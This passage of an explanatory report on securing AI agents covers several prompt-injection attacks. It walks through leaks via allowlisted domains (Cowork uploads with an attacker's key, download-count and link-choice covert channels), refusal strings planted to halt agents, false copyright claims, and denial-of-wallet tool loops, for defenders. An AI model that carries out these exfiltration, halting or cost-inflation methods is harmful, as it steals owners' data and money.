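Every web request also has a method. GET normally retrieves a page and POST normally sends data, so Codex lets owners allow only GET and two similar methods. This restriction would stop most uploads but not the theft from the shop, in which the agent put the key in the address of a page it fetched. Willison describes a January 2026 case in which GET requests could leak data from Superhuman, an email assistant. The app could load images from `docs.google.com`, and Google Forms, on the same domain, stores data that arrives in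 a GET request. A planted email made the assistant submit the contents of dozens of other emails to the attacker's form. Superhuman fixed the flaw.

Allowlists can also fail through carelessness. In 2025, researchers registered a lapsed domain that Salesforce's agent still trusted and received customer data there. The default allowlist for the browser tool in Google's Antigravity included `webhook.site`, a service that records incoming requests for whoever set up the page. According to OSV's *GHSA-vhw5-3g5m-8ggf* (2026), Claude Code checked only whether an address started with a trusted name, so trusting `docs.example` would also let through `docs.example.attacker.test`, which belongs to someone else.

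### Defaults in three coding agents

| Product | Network access by default | What the owner can change |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Code, on the user's machine | Sandbox off. Once the user turns it on, no domain has approval in advance | Approve domains, or refuse all others without asking |
| Codex app, command line and editor extension | Off | Turn it on, with a proxy and domain rules if wanted |
| Codex cloud | Off | Approve domains and limit methods |
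| Copilot cloud agent | Firewall on, with GitHub's own hosts and a recommended allowlist | Add domains or addresses, or turn the firewall off |

OpenAI has the strictest defaults. OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* says that commands in the local versions of Codex have no network access unless the user enables it. The proxy that applies domain rules is a separate setting, so a user who turns on only network access gets no filtering. Codex cloud also has internet access off by default, which Willison called sensible. According to OpenAI's *Agent internet access*, an owner who turns it on can start with an empty list of allowed domains, a preset list of common sites for downloading software, or unrestricted access.

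Copilot's firewall is on by default, but GitHub always allows the hosts that Copilot uses to interact with GitHub, and the "Comment and Control" attack sent the keys out through them. GitHub's *Organization firewall settings for Copilot cloud agent* (2026) announced in April that a company's administrators could set one policy for all of its projects and stop individual projects from adding domains. Unless they do, each project keeps its own settings.

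Claude Code runs on the developer's computer, and without the sandbox it relies mainly on asking for permission. Anthropic found that users approved about 93% of these requests and became less attentive as they received more of them. The sandbox cut requests by 84% because most commands could run inside it without approval. It's odd that Anthropic leaves the sandbox off by default given those figures, though some common tools, including Docker, don't work inside it.

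Commands and data can still get around the sandbox when it is turned on. It covers commands, but not Claude Code's own tools for reading files and fetching pages, or the user's tool servers. If the sandbox blocks a command, Claude can ask to run it again outside the sandbox. If a required component is missing, or the computer runs Windows without a Linux layer, commands run with no sandbox at all. Anthropic provides settings that disable retries outside the sandbox, refuse unlisted domains without asking the user, and stop Claude Code from starting when the sandbox can't start. An owner who relies on the sandbox to protect a key needs all three settings, and separate rules for the page-fetching tool.

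### The Claude Cowork leak

Anthropic released Claude Cowork as a research preview in January 2026. Cowork ran code in a virtual machine that could reach only a short list of domains. Two days later, PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* showed how an attacker could get files out through one of those domains.

In the demonstration, a user gives Cowork a folder of confidential property files and uploads a Word document from the internet that looks like a skill for analysing real estate. The document contains malicious instructions in one-point white type, along with an API key for the attacker's Anthropic account. When the user asks for an analysis, Cowork reads the document, picks the largest file it can find and uploads it to Anthropic's file-storage service with the attacker's key. The file contains financial figures and partial social security numbers. The attacker can then open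 it in their own account and ask Claude about it.

Cowork must call Anthropic's service to function, so `api.anthropic.com` was on the allowlist. The proxy checked the destination and let the upload through. The upload used an API key that the attacker had supplied, not a stolen one, so the file went to the attacker's account.

Cowork never asked for approval. PromptArmor ran this version on Claude Haiku, and in a second test, with a malicious integration guide, the stronger Opus 4.5 sent out customer records the same way. PromptArmor doesn't say how many attempts either test took. According to PromptArmor, Johann Rehberger had reported the same weakness in Anthropic's chat product before Cowork existed, and Anthropic had acknowledged it without fixing it. At launch, Anthropic advised users to watch for suspicious actions. Willison objected that this was unfair to non-programmers, and the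 demonstration supports him, since the only visible sign was one command inside a collapsed block.

Anthropic fixed the leak by adding a second proxy that intercepts and reads requests to its service. It passes only requests that carry the token Cowork issued for the current session, so it rejects requests that use a key from a document. An upload made with the session's token goes to the user's own account, where the attacker can't read it. The proxy also blocks headers that could make Anthropic's servers fetch something for the attacker.

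Anthropic put this proxy inside the virtual machine because its servers can't distinguish a Cowork request from any other customer's. But Anthropic says that if the agent gained full control of the machine's operating system, only two of the machine's six main isolation measures would still work, because those two run outside it. The new proxy presumably isn't one of them, so it works only if the agent's code doesn't gain that control.

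#### What approving a domain approves

After the leak, Anthropic described its allowlist as a "capability grant", meaning that whoever approves a domain approves every function an agent can reach through it. Anthropic had previously thought of the list as a filter on destinations, but approving `api.anthropic.com` had also allowed agents to upload files to any Anthropic account.

Anthropic's custom proxy worked as designed, and a flawless proxy with the same rule would have leaked the same file. Anthropic nevertheless calls the proxy the part that failed, while the standard isolation software around it held. Testing whether a proxy blocks unlisted sites won't reveal a flaw in the rule. An owner has to check, for each listed site, whether a stranger could have an account there and what that account could reveal about the agent's requests.

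The shop's payment service fails that test, because the attacker can open an account there too. A payload could supply the attacker's payment key and have the agent write customer details into a record on the attacker's account. A broker that replaces whatever key is in the request, as Docker's does, would prevent this by sending the record to the shop's account. A broker that only fills in placeholders might let the attacker's key through, unless a separate rule rejects other keys.

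### CVE-2026-54316: a leak through download counts

Claude Code's WebFetch tool reads web pages for the model, and Anthropic had approved some sites in advance so that the tool could fetch them without asking for permission. One was Hugging Face, where anyone can publish files. MITRE's *Claude Code* (2026), the official record of the flaw, explains that the approval covered the whole hostname, including any project an attacker published there. Restrictions that a user had placed on the agent's tools also didn't apply to these fetches.

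Hugging Face counts the downloads of each project's files. A payload could make the agent download files from the attacker's projects in a pattern that encoded a secret, which the attacker could then work out from the counts. The record lists files, environment variables and command output among the data at risk. Because the agent uploaded nothing and put no secret in any address, a rule allowing only GET requests would have let every request through, and a scanner looking for the key in outgoing traffic would have found nothing.

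The flaw affected versions from 0.2.54 up to, but not including, 2.1.163. GitLab's *CVE-2026-54316* (2026) reproduces Anthropic's June 17 advisory, which credits the security company Novee. According to the advisory, users with automatic updates already had the fix. As of June 23, the official record rated the severity at 6.0 out of 10 and listed no known exploitation.

That rating may understate what Novee found. *Black Hat 2026* (Underhill, 2026) links this CVE to Novee's August research on stealing credentials through a planted issue, and adds that the attack ran code on Anthropic's build server. The official record describes only the Hugging Face channel and doesn't mention running code, so someone using it alone to decide how urgently to update would see only a medium-severity leak.

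### How much a narrow channel can carry

The advisory gives no figure for how much data an attacker could extract through download counts, but a calculation gives an upper limit for channels of this kind. Suppose the shop's key has 40 random characters, each drawn from 64 symbols. Each character holds log₂ 64 = 6 bits, so the key holds 40 × 6 = 240 bits. If the agent can write any address, it can put all 240 bits in a single request.

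An agent that can fetch only 1,024 approved pages, and can't change their addresses, can still leak the key if the attacker sees which pages it fetches and in what order. The agent can encode the key in its choice of pages without writing it anywhere. Each choice carries log₂ 1,024 = 10 bits, so 24 requests are enough to send the whole key.

| Pages to choose from | Bits per request | Requests for the whole key | Most that ten requests can leak |
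|---|---|---|---|
| 2 | 1 | 240 | 10 bits |
| 26 | 4.7 | 52 | 47 bits |
| 64 | 6 | 40 | 60 bits |
| 1,024 | 10 | 24 | 100 bits |

Capping the number of requests protects the key better than shortening the list of allowed pages. Cutting the list from 1,024 pages to 64 raises the number of requests needed to leak the key only from 24 to 40. With 1,024 pages and a cap of ten requests, the attacker learns at most 100 of the key's 240 bits, which leaves 2¹⁴⁰ possible keys (about 10⁴²), far too many to try.

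The cap has to apply to the key rather than to each session. If the count resets every morning, the agent could send the rest of the key on the second and third days. The 100-bit limit also assumes that the attacker learns nothing from the timing of the requests, since an agent that chooses when to send each one can convey extra information. An attacker who sees only totals, such as download counts, cannot tell what order the requests came in, so ten requests would carry about 78 bits.

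A cap on requests gives short secrets almost no protection. A six-digit login code has a million possible values, or about 20 bits, so two requests, each to one of 1,024 pages, would be enough to leak it.

Ayush Paul demonstrated a channel of this kind against Claude's chat app, in an attack that Willison described in July 2026. The app's fetching tool opened only addresses that the user had typed, that a search had returned or that appeared on a page it had already fetched, not addresses that Claude had composed itself. Paul set up a site where each page had a link for every letter of the alphabet, and a payload that made Claude spell out what it knew about the user by following the links. Paul obtained the user's name, home city and employer.

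The tool's design blocks the usual theft, in which the agent writes a secret into a URL. But an attacker could supply all the URLs in advance and learn the secret from which ones Claude opened. Anthropic said it had already found the problem internally, and fixed it by no longer letting the tool open links from pages it had fetched. This also makes the tool less useful for legitimate research, which usually involves following links.

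Developers who use the fetching tool in their own software can set an allowlist and a maximum number of fetches. Willison's example sets the maximum at five. If an attacker encodes data in the choice among 1,024 pages, each fetch would leak at most 10 bits, and five fetches at most 50. Willison also noted that the tool trusts any address in the user's message. Many applications paste strangers' text into that message, as Cline's did with issue titles, so the tool trusts addresses in that text too.

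### Rules that follow the data

A proxy applies the same rule to a public weather report as to the shop's customer list. Another approach is to label each piece of data and check the label whenever the agent tries to send that data somewhere. In 2025, Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues at Google, Google DeepMind and ETH Zurich described such a system, CaMeL, in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design*.

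Suppose the owner asks the agent to find the bookkeeper's address in the shop's email and send the week's sales there. CaMeL would handle the request in four steps:

1. A planning model reads the owner's request, but none of the email, and writes a short program that searches the inbox, extracts the address, gets the sales figures and sends them.
2. A second model reads the email and extracts the address. This model can't call any tools.
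3. Ordinary software runs the program and labels every value with its origin and with the people who may read it.
4. Before each tool call, the software compares the labels with the owner's policy. If the sales figures would reach someone who may not read them, it refuses or asks the owner.

A planted email can't add a step to the program, because the planning model finished writing it before anything opened the email. The email can still corrupt a value, though. If it causes the second model to return the attacker's address, the program will try to send the sales figures there, and only the fourth step prevents the leak. Any value computed from the figures inherits their labels and restrictions, so encoding the figures or splitting them up doesn't remove the restrictions.

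With CaMeL, an agent completed 77% of the tasks in AgentDojo with a provable security guarantee, compared with 84% for an undefended agent. The guarantee holds however persuasive a payload is, which an attack success rate can't establish. It covers the tool calls that the policy governs but not the text of the agent's answers, so a planted email could still make the agent report false sales figures to the owner without making a forbidden tool call.

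The loss of seven percentage points is small for a guarantee of that kind, but results on AgentDojo may overstate how well the design works. CaMeL works well when a model can plan the task from the request alone, but badly when the next step depends on what a document says, for example when the owner asks the agent to do whatever the supplier's latest email requires. CaMeL also used nearly three times as many tokens as an ordinary agent, and someone has to write the policies. Under strict policies, the agent asks the owner for approval more often, which is a weak safeguard when people approve 93% of requests. The models tested are now old, and a newer planning model would probably write fewer faulty programs, but it couldn't complete tasks that the policy blocks.

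Some leaks get around the labels. If a program fetches an outside page once for every unpaid invoice, whoever runs that page can learn the number of invoices by counting the visits, even though the program sent no labelled value. Debenedetti and colleagues discuss such leaks and offer a stricter mode that prevents some of them by treating everything inside such a loop as dependent on the secret. The stricter mode also blocks more legitimate work.

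Manuel Costa and colleagues at Microsoft proposed a more flexible system, FIDES, in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, also from 2025. Its planning model can choose each step as results come in. The software hides untrusted results behind named placeholders, which the model can pass to tools without reading the contents. If the model needs to read them, the software marks the whole context as untrusted and then blocks consequential actions, such as sending money. Separate labels record who may read each piece of data. The shop's agent could issue refunds, but not after reading a supplier's page.

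### Payloads on approved sites

An allowlist limits who can receive the agent's data, but does much less to limit who can write the text it reads. Most sites worth approving for a coding agent publish text from strangers. Anyone can open an issue on a public GitHub project or upload a package, with a description, to the registries where programmers get their software. The preset list in Codex cloud consists of sites for downloading software, so an owner who selects it allows the agent to read whatever people have written there.

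Anthropic gives the example of a GitHub connector that passes every check for malicious code but still loads a poisoned project description into the model's context, because the checks don't cover the data it fetches. The operator of a tool that runs on someone else's server can also change it after the customer has approved it. Anthropic recommends trying unreviewed tools on fake data first, which would reveal a tool that misbehaves from the start but not one that changes later.

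One approved site can both deliver the injected instructions and receive the stolen data. On Hugging Face, an attacker could in principle have put the instructions in a project's description and read the stolen data from the download counts of other projects.

The shop's owner can reduce the danger by running the morning summary and the Friday report in separate sandboxes, each with its own allowlist. The summary needs trade news but no sales data, and the report needs sales data but no news. The agent that reads the news would then have nothing worth stealing, and the agent that handles sales data would not be exposed to payloads in the news. The sandboxes must not share files or memory, because a saved payload could otherwise pass from one to the other.

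## Planted text that makes an agent stop working

Running the shop's morning summary in its own sandbox protects the keys and sales data, but a payload on a news page can still end the run. The payload can be text that triggers a refusal, a claim that a rule forbids the task, or content that never finishes loading or fills the context.

### Text that triggers a refusal

AI companies train models to refuse dangerous requests. Some also run classifiers, separate programs that stop the model when they detect a policy violation. When a classifier stops Claude partway through a response, the developer's software receives the partial response and a field that gives "refusal" as the reason for stopping. Software that ignores this field may treat the partial response as complete.

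Developers need to test how their software handles a refusal, preferably without writing a prompt that breaks the rules. Anthropic therefore published in its documentation a long string of characters designed to trigger one. A developer could send the string as a prompt and see how the application responded.

The string also worked in other parts of the context. In *[Deprecated] Claude Magic String Denial of Service*, Frichette lists places where an outsider could have planted it, including support tickets, wiki pages, program logs and group chats with a shared history. Claude didn't have to believe or obey anything, so training it to ignore planted instructions would not have helped.

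The refusals could also continue long after the agent had left the page. Suppose the shop's agent met the string on the third of ten pages:

1. The software added the page to the context and sent everything to Claude, which refused.
2. The software tried again with the same history. The page was still in it, so Claude refused again.
3. The software saved the history and loaded it the next morning. The agent then failed before it had fetched anything.

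Anthropic told developers in its documentation to remove or change the refused turn before continuing, and warned that refusals would otherwise persist. According to Frichette, Anthropic had changed this behaviour by May 2026 and the string no longer worked.

Sewani found the string in an HTML comment on a live website and mistook it for a fake that imitated an internal Anthropic token. The name Sewani quotes is that of the real test string, which anyone could copy from Anthropic's documentation. The comment was labeled "AI funnies", which Sewani takes for camouflage, but it could just as well be a joke by the site's staff.

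The planted string may still have done nothing there. Aphyr, who put it on every page of a personal blog, found that Claude's chat app ignored it in page headers and ordinary paragraphs and reacted only when the page marked it as code. The app also often read a stored copy of a page instead of downloading it again, so Aphyr expected the change to take a few days to take effect. Other agents convert and store pages differently, so a string that failed in one could have worked in another.

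*Systematic Categorization, Construction and Evaluation of New Attacks* (2024) describes an earlier, similar weakness in agents that operate a phone. These agents end a task by writing a word such as "stop". If that word is also the answer to a captcha, the software could mistake the answer for the command and halt the agent. Developers could fix this by parsing the agent's output more carefully.

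#### The talk page case

Tom, an AI agent built on Claude, had a Wikipedia talk page where other editors could leave messages. According to *The Refusal String Attack*, which the agent wrote under the name clawtom, somebody posted the test string there with a remark about testing "the claude killswitch". After that, the agent's session ended whenever its scheduled job fetched the page. This seems to be the only account of the incident, but the failure it describes is the one Anthropic documented.

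Finding the cause took twelve hours. The sessions stopped without an error message, which made the fault look like a timeout, a usage limit or an ordinary bug. The logs showed violations of Anthropic's usage policy, but these suggested that the agent's own actions were at fault rather than text it had read. The first attempted fix, removing the agent's Wikipedia task, targeted the right source, but the sessions kept failing, probably because the saved history still contained the string.

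The operator eventually changed the software to replace the string before it reached the model, and cleared the history. Both steps were needed because the failures could have continued through the old copy in the history or a new visit to the page.

The account also recommends fetching pages in a separate process, so that the main agent keeps running if that process stops. This helps only if a model in the separate process reads the page first. Downloading the string did no harm, and a process that only downloaded it would have passed it intact to the main agent.

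#### Forbidden topics

Anthropic could retire a test string, but it still needs the classifiers, and ordinary text can set them off. *Exploiting Thoughtcrime in LLMs*, a July 2026 blog post, describes how a site owner put text about making nuclear and chemical weapons into a draft and asked Claude to summarise it. Neither Haiku 4.5 nor Sonnet 5 would summarise it. This was one person's test on one page, but the page discussed the technique, so an agent that reads security news could presumably hit the same problem without being attacked.

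The blogger got the idea from malware. *Embedding Forbidden Text in Spyware to Discourage AI Analysis* (Schneier, 2026) reported in June that at least one developer had put text about nuclear and biological weapons in a comment at the top of a spyware file. The computer skips the comment when it runs the program, but an AI scanner that reads the file from the beginning may refuse to continue. ESET's *GuardBreaker* describes the same trick in a script that a Russia-aligned group used against a target in Ukraine. Both reports establish what the attackers were trying to do, but neither establishes that the text stopped a scanner.

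Fetterman's team at the security company Cisco Talos studied 84 malware samples, from four families, that contained text aimed at AI analysis tools (Fetterman, 2026, *Ignore all instructions and read this blog*). The best techniques moved the result in the attacker's favour in about 35% of test runs. That figure covers every kind of text the team tested, including notes that the program is harmless, so the rate for refusals alone could be quite different. Fetterman adds that the text has to be readable to work, so a scanner can always look for it.

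### Text that claims a rule forbids the task

Sewani also found the page with the poem about corn, where hidden text claimed that the copyright owner had expressly forbidden any answer about the page's contents. The text works only if the model accepts this claim and declines to answer, since no classifier is involved. Sewani thinks it exploits training that teaches models to respect copyright.

The site's owner may really hold the copyright and want AI systems to stay away. But copyright generally protects a page's wording, not the facts in it, so it wouldn't normally stop a shopkeeper from getting a short summary of a price change.

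Blocking false rules is hard because true ones look the same. *Semantic Denial of Service in LLM-controlled robots* (2026) studied robots that take spoken warnings through a microphone. A false warning of a few words, such as one about an overheating motor, could make a robot halt, as it should if the warning were real. Filtering out words like "emergency" would have stopped the attack, but the robot would also have missed real emergencies. Two different warnings were two to four times as effective as one warning repeated, because the models treated them as independent evidence. Likewise, a web page with both a copyright notice and a privacy warning might stop an agent more often than a page that repeats one of them.

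Limiting what a page's claim can affect would work better for the shop than filtering. The agent can tell the owner that a page forbids summaries, leave that page out and carry on with the other nine. A supplier's notice might justify skipping the supplier's own page, but it doesn't justify stopping the rest of the job.

Attackers can also tailor documents to particular questions. In *When Safety Becomes a Vulnerability* (2026), an attacker uses a model to write a document that makes a question-answering system refuse a harmless question. The model refines the document on a practice system, and the document is then planted in the real system, which the attacker has never tested. *Beyond Explicit Refusals* (2026) describes documents that lead to evasive answers instead. The system says that the subject is controversial and the sources conflict, and recommends looking elsewhere. These answers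 don't help the user, and a developer who counts refusals would miss them.

### Content that never ends or fills the context

Google found a site where text on an ordinary page is meant to lure AI readers to a second page, which sends a stream of text that never ends. Google thinks the site's author hoped to waste resources or cause timeouts.

An agent that waits for the whole page will wait forever, so its page-fetching tool needs a time limit. The limit has to apply to the whole download. Many programs restart the clock whenever new data arrives, and a server could keep such a program waiting indefinitely by sending one character every few seconds.

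A time limit alone isn't enough if the server is fast. At 100,000 characters per second, a 30-second limit would let through three million characters. At roughly four characters per token, that is about 750,000 tokens, which would fill many models' contexts. The tool therefore also needs a size limit that applies before the text reaches the model.

Attackers can also exploit size limits. ESET mentions an npm package whose main file repeated a short phrase tens of thousands of times ahead of its malicious script, apparently to use up the scanner's context before it reached the script. If a scanner reads only the first part of such a file, it can miss the script and report that it found nothing. The tool has to record that it cut the file short, and the scanner has to treat the result as an incomplete check.

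### What AgentDojo's tests found

In *AgentDojo*, the paper on the simulated office and bank that CAISI used, Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues (2024) tried several texts meant only to make an agent stop. One was a plain request to stop. Others contained swearing directed at the agent, a captcha, an instruction to write an abusive email, or a claim that what it was reading was illegal. None was more effective at derailing the agent than an ordinary payload that gave it a malicious task.

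For comparison, the GPT-4o agent failed 31% of its tasks with no attack. With ordinary payloads, the failure rate was between 31% and 33% for three common ones and about 50% for the strongest. AgentDojo counts a task as failed if the agent also did something malicious, so the agent may have finished the user's work in some of those cases.

*Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) also found that in some AgentDojo tasks, the payload replaces information the agent needs, such as the details of a bill it has to pay. The agent then fails however well it resists the planted instruction. A real attacker who can edit the bill could cause the same failure, but the failure is weak evidence about the model's resistance to injection.

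GPT-4o is now old, and *Exploring the Hidden Cost of the World Around AI Agents* (2026) tested newer models. It placed AgentDojo's own attack in ten tasks and ran each task four times, with extra rules in the system prompt. No model followed the planted instructions. The test counted only whether a model obeyed the planted text, so a model could have ignored the attack and still failed to finish its task.

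Some defences cause outages themselves. AgentDojo includes a detector that aborts the task when it flags a tool result as an injection. *Indirect Prompt Injections* reports that GPT-4o under attack completed about 61% of its tasks without the detector and 32% with it. An attacker who can't get past such a detector can deliberately set it off to stop the task. Repeating the user's request after each tool result instead raised completion to about 70%, though a payload designed to counter that defence might undo the gain.

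### Why site owners plant such text

Many of the people who plant such text are trying to keep AI systems away from their own writing. The usual method is a robots.txt file, which asks automated visitors to stay out, backed by a list of visitors to block. Go Make Things' *poisoning the ai well* explains why its author gave up on this method. The list is never finished, because some AI crawlers don't identify themselves, some do so only after copying much of the web, and new ones keep appearing.

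In *consent llm scrapers and poisoning the well*, Bailey wanted protection that needed no upkeep and didn't get in the way of human readers. Bailey's idea was to plant an instruction in each post and hide it from screen readers, which read pages aloud to blind people. The instruction asks for a very long and expensive output, so it is closer to an attempt to run up a bill than to a request to leave.

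These owners have a reasonable complaint and are acting on their own sites, which is much easier to defend than putting the test string on somebody else's talk page. But planted text works poorly against the crawlers that bother them most. A crawler that collects training data can copy a page without any model reading it, so the text may have no immediate effect. When a person asks an assistant to explain the page, the assistant does read the text, and the person gets no answer. Aphyr's use of the string made more sense because it was meant to reduce spam produced with language models, and a spamming agent may well read a post before commenting on it.

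An agent's owner can respect the objection without losing a day's work by having the agent skip the page and name it in its summary. The site's author then keeps the agent out, and the shopkeeper can open the page in a browser.

### Recovering from a halt

Anthropic's *Handle streaming refusals* warns that a refusal arrives as a successful response, so monitoring only error rates won't catch it. In a batch of requests, a refused one comes back marked "succeeded". In Claude Managed Agents, the session goes idle after a refusal, and the stated reason can be the same as for a normal end of turn. The developer has to check a second field for details of the refusal, though that field can be empty.

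| What goes wrong | Remedy | What the remedy can miss |
|---|---|---|
| The software takes a refusal for a finished task | Check the reason for stopping after every response | Refusals and evasions written as ordinary text |
| The refused item stays in the history | Remove it before trying again | Copies in saved memory or in a condensed history |
| A page never finishes loading | Limit the total time for each fetch | A fast page that sends too much |
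| A page fills the context | Limit its size and record the cut | Anything after the cut |
| One item stops the whole job | Skip it, or send it to a fallback | Payloads that the fallback obeys |
| Nobody notices the outage | Send an alert when refusals rise | A single well-chosen item |

Anthropic says developers can remove the turn that caused the refusal, rephrase it or clear the whole conversation. Clearing everything is simplest, but it discards the pages the agent has already read. If the shop's agent refuses right after the third page arrives, the software can replace that page with a note that it was skipped and continue. When several pages arrive together, the software can test half of them, then keep halving the group that contains the page causing the refusal. If one of 16 pages is responsible, this takes four tests.

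Filtering out a known string is easy and would have prevented the talk page failures. It doesn't work against forbidden topics or invented rules, because an attacker can word them in many different ways.

Anthropic also recommends trying another Claude model for refused requests, because the same model will usually refuse again. This keeps a service running, but it may let an attacker influence which model reads the page, and models differ greatly in how well they resist injection. A page could contain one passage that makes the main model refuse and another that tries to hijack the fallback. Removing the suspect page before retrying, or giving the fallback model no tools, would be safer.

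Frichette recommends an alert when refusals spike, and setting aside sessions that refuse repeatedly. A large service can compare today's refusal rate with its usual one. The shop has too few requests for that, but the owner can compare the summary with the list of links. If the summary covers only nine of ten links, the missing page needs checking, whatever reason the agent gave. This check also catches a page that never loaded, but not a summary that mentions a page without saying anything useful about it.

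### When a reviewing agent halts

Skipping a page is usually harmless when an agent summarises the news, but skipping an item may be what the attacker wants when an agent reviews code, scans for malware or moderates comments. In *Hard-stopping AI agent pipelines with prompt-level kill switches*, Olejnik describes an automated review that ends at the first refusal. The model never chooses the next step, the checks never run, and the log can look like that of a normal review.

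The developer has to decide in advance what happens to an item if the reviewer halts. Letting it through (failing open) means an attacker can get past the review by halting the reviewer. Blocking it (failing closed) protects whatever lies behind the review but lets an attacker hold up other people's work. *From Shield to Target* (Zhou, Wang and colleagues, 2026) points out that limiting how long a safety check may run doesn't avoid this choice, because the system still needs a rule for when the limit runs out.

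The damage from text that halts an agent depends on how much work the system blocks in response. Suppose an outsider puts such text in a proposed change to the shop's website code. If the system holds only that change, the attacker has delayed only their own work. But if the reviewing agent processes all the day's changes in one context, the text can stop every one of them. The agent should therefore review each item in its own session.

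Separate sessions don't help when several people write in the same item. A stranger could leave a comment with a trigger under an honest developer's change, and a rule that blocks the item would also block the developer's change. The system could instead remove the stranger's comment and review the change without it. In a group chat, it could remove only the message with the trigger.

Olejnik advises recording the result as "assessment incomplete" and sending the item through another route, such as a filter that doesn't use a language model. This works fairly well for malware. Schneier's post notes that conventional detection methods, such as matching known patterns in the code or watching what the program does, still work on files with forbidden text. A scanner can also treat a comment about nuclear weapons at the top of a script as suspicious, but that alone shouldn't be enough to classify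 the file as malware, since articles and test files about these attacks contain the same text.

Comments and customer messages often need human judgement, and an attacker can overload the people who review them. Suppose a moderation agent handles 1,000 comments a day and halts on ten, which staff check by hand. If someone posts 500 comments that each contain text that triggers a halt, staff have about 510 to check. A limit on held items per account would contain the attack, at least until the attacker opens more accounts. Keeping held items in a separate queue also helps, because ordinary comments can still go through while staff catch up.

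The right default depends on which mistake would do more harm. A shop can publish a customer's review a day late without much harm, so it makes sense to hold a review that halts the moderator. An urgent message about a faulty product shouldn't wait, so if the agent that sorts the shop's email refuses to read one, the software should deliver it to the owner unread, with a warning, and block every agent from acting on it.

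## Planted text that makes an agent run up costs

If a payload halts the shop's agent, the owner gets no summary and has a reason to investigate. A denial-of-wallet attack can run up costs while the agent still delivers its usual summary, in which case the bill is the only sign of trouble.

Developers usually pay a model provider for every token the model reads, and a higher price for every token it writes. A turn is one request to the model and its response. Planted text can raise an agent's bill by increasing the number of turns it takes, the amount the model writes in each one and the amount of earlier text it has to read again.

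### Tool loops and hidden reasoning

In 2023, Johann Rehberger, writing as wunderwuzzi23, showed in *LLM Apps* that planted text could make ChatGPT call a tool repeatedly. The risk to subscribers was small because OpenAI paid for the extra work, ChatGPT seemed to stop after ten calls per message, and the user could press a stop button. Rehberger was more worried about automated services that read untrusted text and call tools. The shop's agent is one of these services. It runs unattended, and its owner pays for every token.

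In *Breaking Agents*, Zhang, Tan and colleagues (2024) studied such loops systematically. They made agents either repeat an action until reaching their iteration limit or take harmless but irrelevant steps. In several scenarios, more than 80% of tasks failed. Instructions in the user's own request worked better than instructions in tool results, so the highest failure rates are weak evidence about planted web pages. The models tested are also now old. The failures were easy to see, and an owner whose agent failed that often would soon look for the cause.

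A later attack, *OverThink* (Kumar, Roh and colleagues, 2025), made models use more reasoning tokens while keeping their answers correct. Reasoning models write out intermediate steps before they answer, and providers charge for these steps but often hide them from users. The attack planted decoy problems in text that a model would retrieve. The model worked through the decoy, then answered the user's question. Reasoning tokens rose 13-fold and 46-fold on two sets of factual questions, and 12-fold on a set of longer puzzles. In one example, when asked what year the first human landed on Mars, the model correctly answered that nobody has, but it used 10,624 reasoning tokens instead of 384.

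A developer can't judge the cost of a page by how hard it looks. Three reasoning models used about 21,000 tokens on an average Sudoku but only about 8,900 on an average problem from the 2024 International Mathematical Olympiad. Kumar and colleagues suspect that models reason longest on problems with many small steps they can check.

The attack also worked on coding agents that read poisoned skills, project descriptions or code. The largest increase was 17-fold according to the paper's abstract and 12.7-fold according to its introduction. The extra reasoning has to fit into the model's responses, and developers can cap the length of each response, so an attacker needs more turns to get past the cap.

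### A tool that postpones its answer

Zhou, Zheng and colleagues (2026), in *Beyond Max Tokens*, got those turns by controlling a tool. Suppose the shop's agent uses an outside provider's MCP server to convert suppliers' prices into pounds, and an attacker has taken over that server:

1. The agent asks the server to convert a price, as it does every morning.
2. The server replies that the job is still in progress and that the agent has to call again. Each new call must include a long piece of text, which the model has to write.
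3. The agent complies, and the server gives the same kind of reply for several rounds.
4. The server returns the correct price, and the agent finishes the summary.

The tool keeps its name and functions, and the final answer is correct. The developer wrongly assumed that a correct answer meant a reasonable amount of work.

Zhou and colleagues tested six models on two benchmarks of tool use, ToolBench and BFCL, with 464 requests in all. An attack counted as successful only if the agent made the long series of calls and also completed the user's task. These are the ToolBench results:

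| Model | Output tokens, normal | Output tokens, attacked | Increase | Tasks completed, normal | Attack succeeded and task completed |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Llama-3.3-70B | 260 | 81,830 | 315× | 98.1% | 96.2% |
| Mistral Large | 127 | 61,354 | 483× | 90.8% | 81.2% |
| Llama-DeepSeek-70B | 197 | 65,546 | 333× | 86.6% | 78.9% |
| Qwen3-32B | 638 | 65,273 | 102× | 94.6% | 80.5% |
| GLM-4.5-Air | 634 | 63,694 | 100× | 95.0% | 83.1% |
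| Seed-32B | 1,298 | 85,037 | 66× | 90.4% | 84.3% |

The largest increase was on BFCL, where Mistral Large wrote 57,255 tokens per request instead of 87, or 658 times as many. The multiple is this large mostly because Mistral Large normally writes so little. Across both benchmarks, attacked models wrote between about 57,000 and 90,000 tokens, a much narrower range than that of the multiples. Seed-32B wrote the most under attack but had the smallest multiple because its normal answers are long. The absolute cost is therefore more useful to an owner than the multiple.

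Zhou and colleagues found that the attack also slowed ordinary requests running on the same machines to about half their usual speed. A company that hosts its own model could therefore have an outage as well as a larger electricity bill.

Detection mostly failed. A filter for unusual-looking text flagged nothing. The researchers also asked the models to check their own behaviour and used two safety models to review the full record of each run, but these checks flagged less than 3% of the attacks. The safety models are designed to detect harmful content, and the text of the records contained none.

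The study has important limits. It ran in a simulator with placeholder tool results, on simple tasks that each needed one tool, and it tested models from 2024 and 2025. The attacker also had to control the tool server, which is much harder than planting text on a page.

### How the cost adds up

A model that may write at most *M* tokens per turn can write up to *nM* tokens in *n* turns. If the software keeps everything in the context, the model also rereads its earlier output: up to *M* tokens on the second turn, 2*M* on the third, and so on up to (*n* − 1)*M* on the last. These add up to at most *Mn*(*n* − 1)/2 input tokens.

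Zhou and colleagues set *M* at 16,384. Over five turns, the model can write 81,920 tokens (5 × 16,384) and reread 163,840 (10 × 16,384).

| Turns | Most the model can write | Most it rereads of its own output |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | 16,384 | 0 |
| 5 | 81,920 | 163,840 |
| 10 | 163,840 | 737,280 |
| 20 | 327,680 | 3,112,960 |

Doubling the turns from five to ten doubles the output but multiplies the rereading by 4.5. The last row requires a model that can hold more than 311,000 tokens of history, and some models can't hold that much.

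At an assumed price of $10 per million output tokens, the 81,830 tokens that Llama-3.3-70B wrote under attack would cost about 82 cents, compared with about a quarter of a cent for its normal 260. For 1,000 requests, that is $818 instead of $2.60. At an assumed $2 per million input tokens, rereading 163,840 tokens would add another 33 cents to a request, though many providers discount text they have recently processed.

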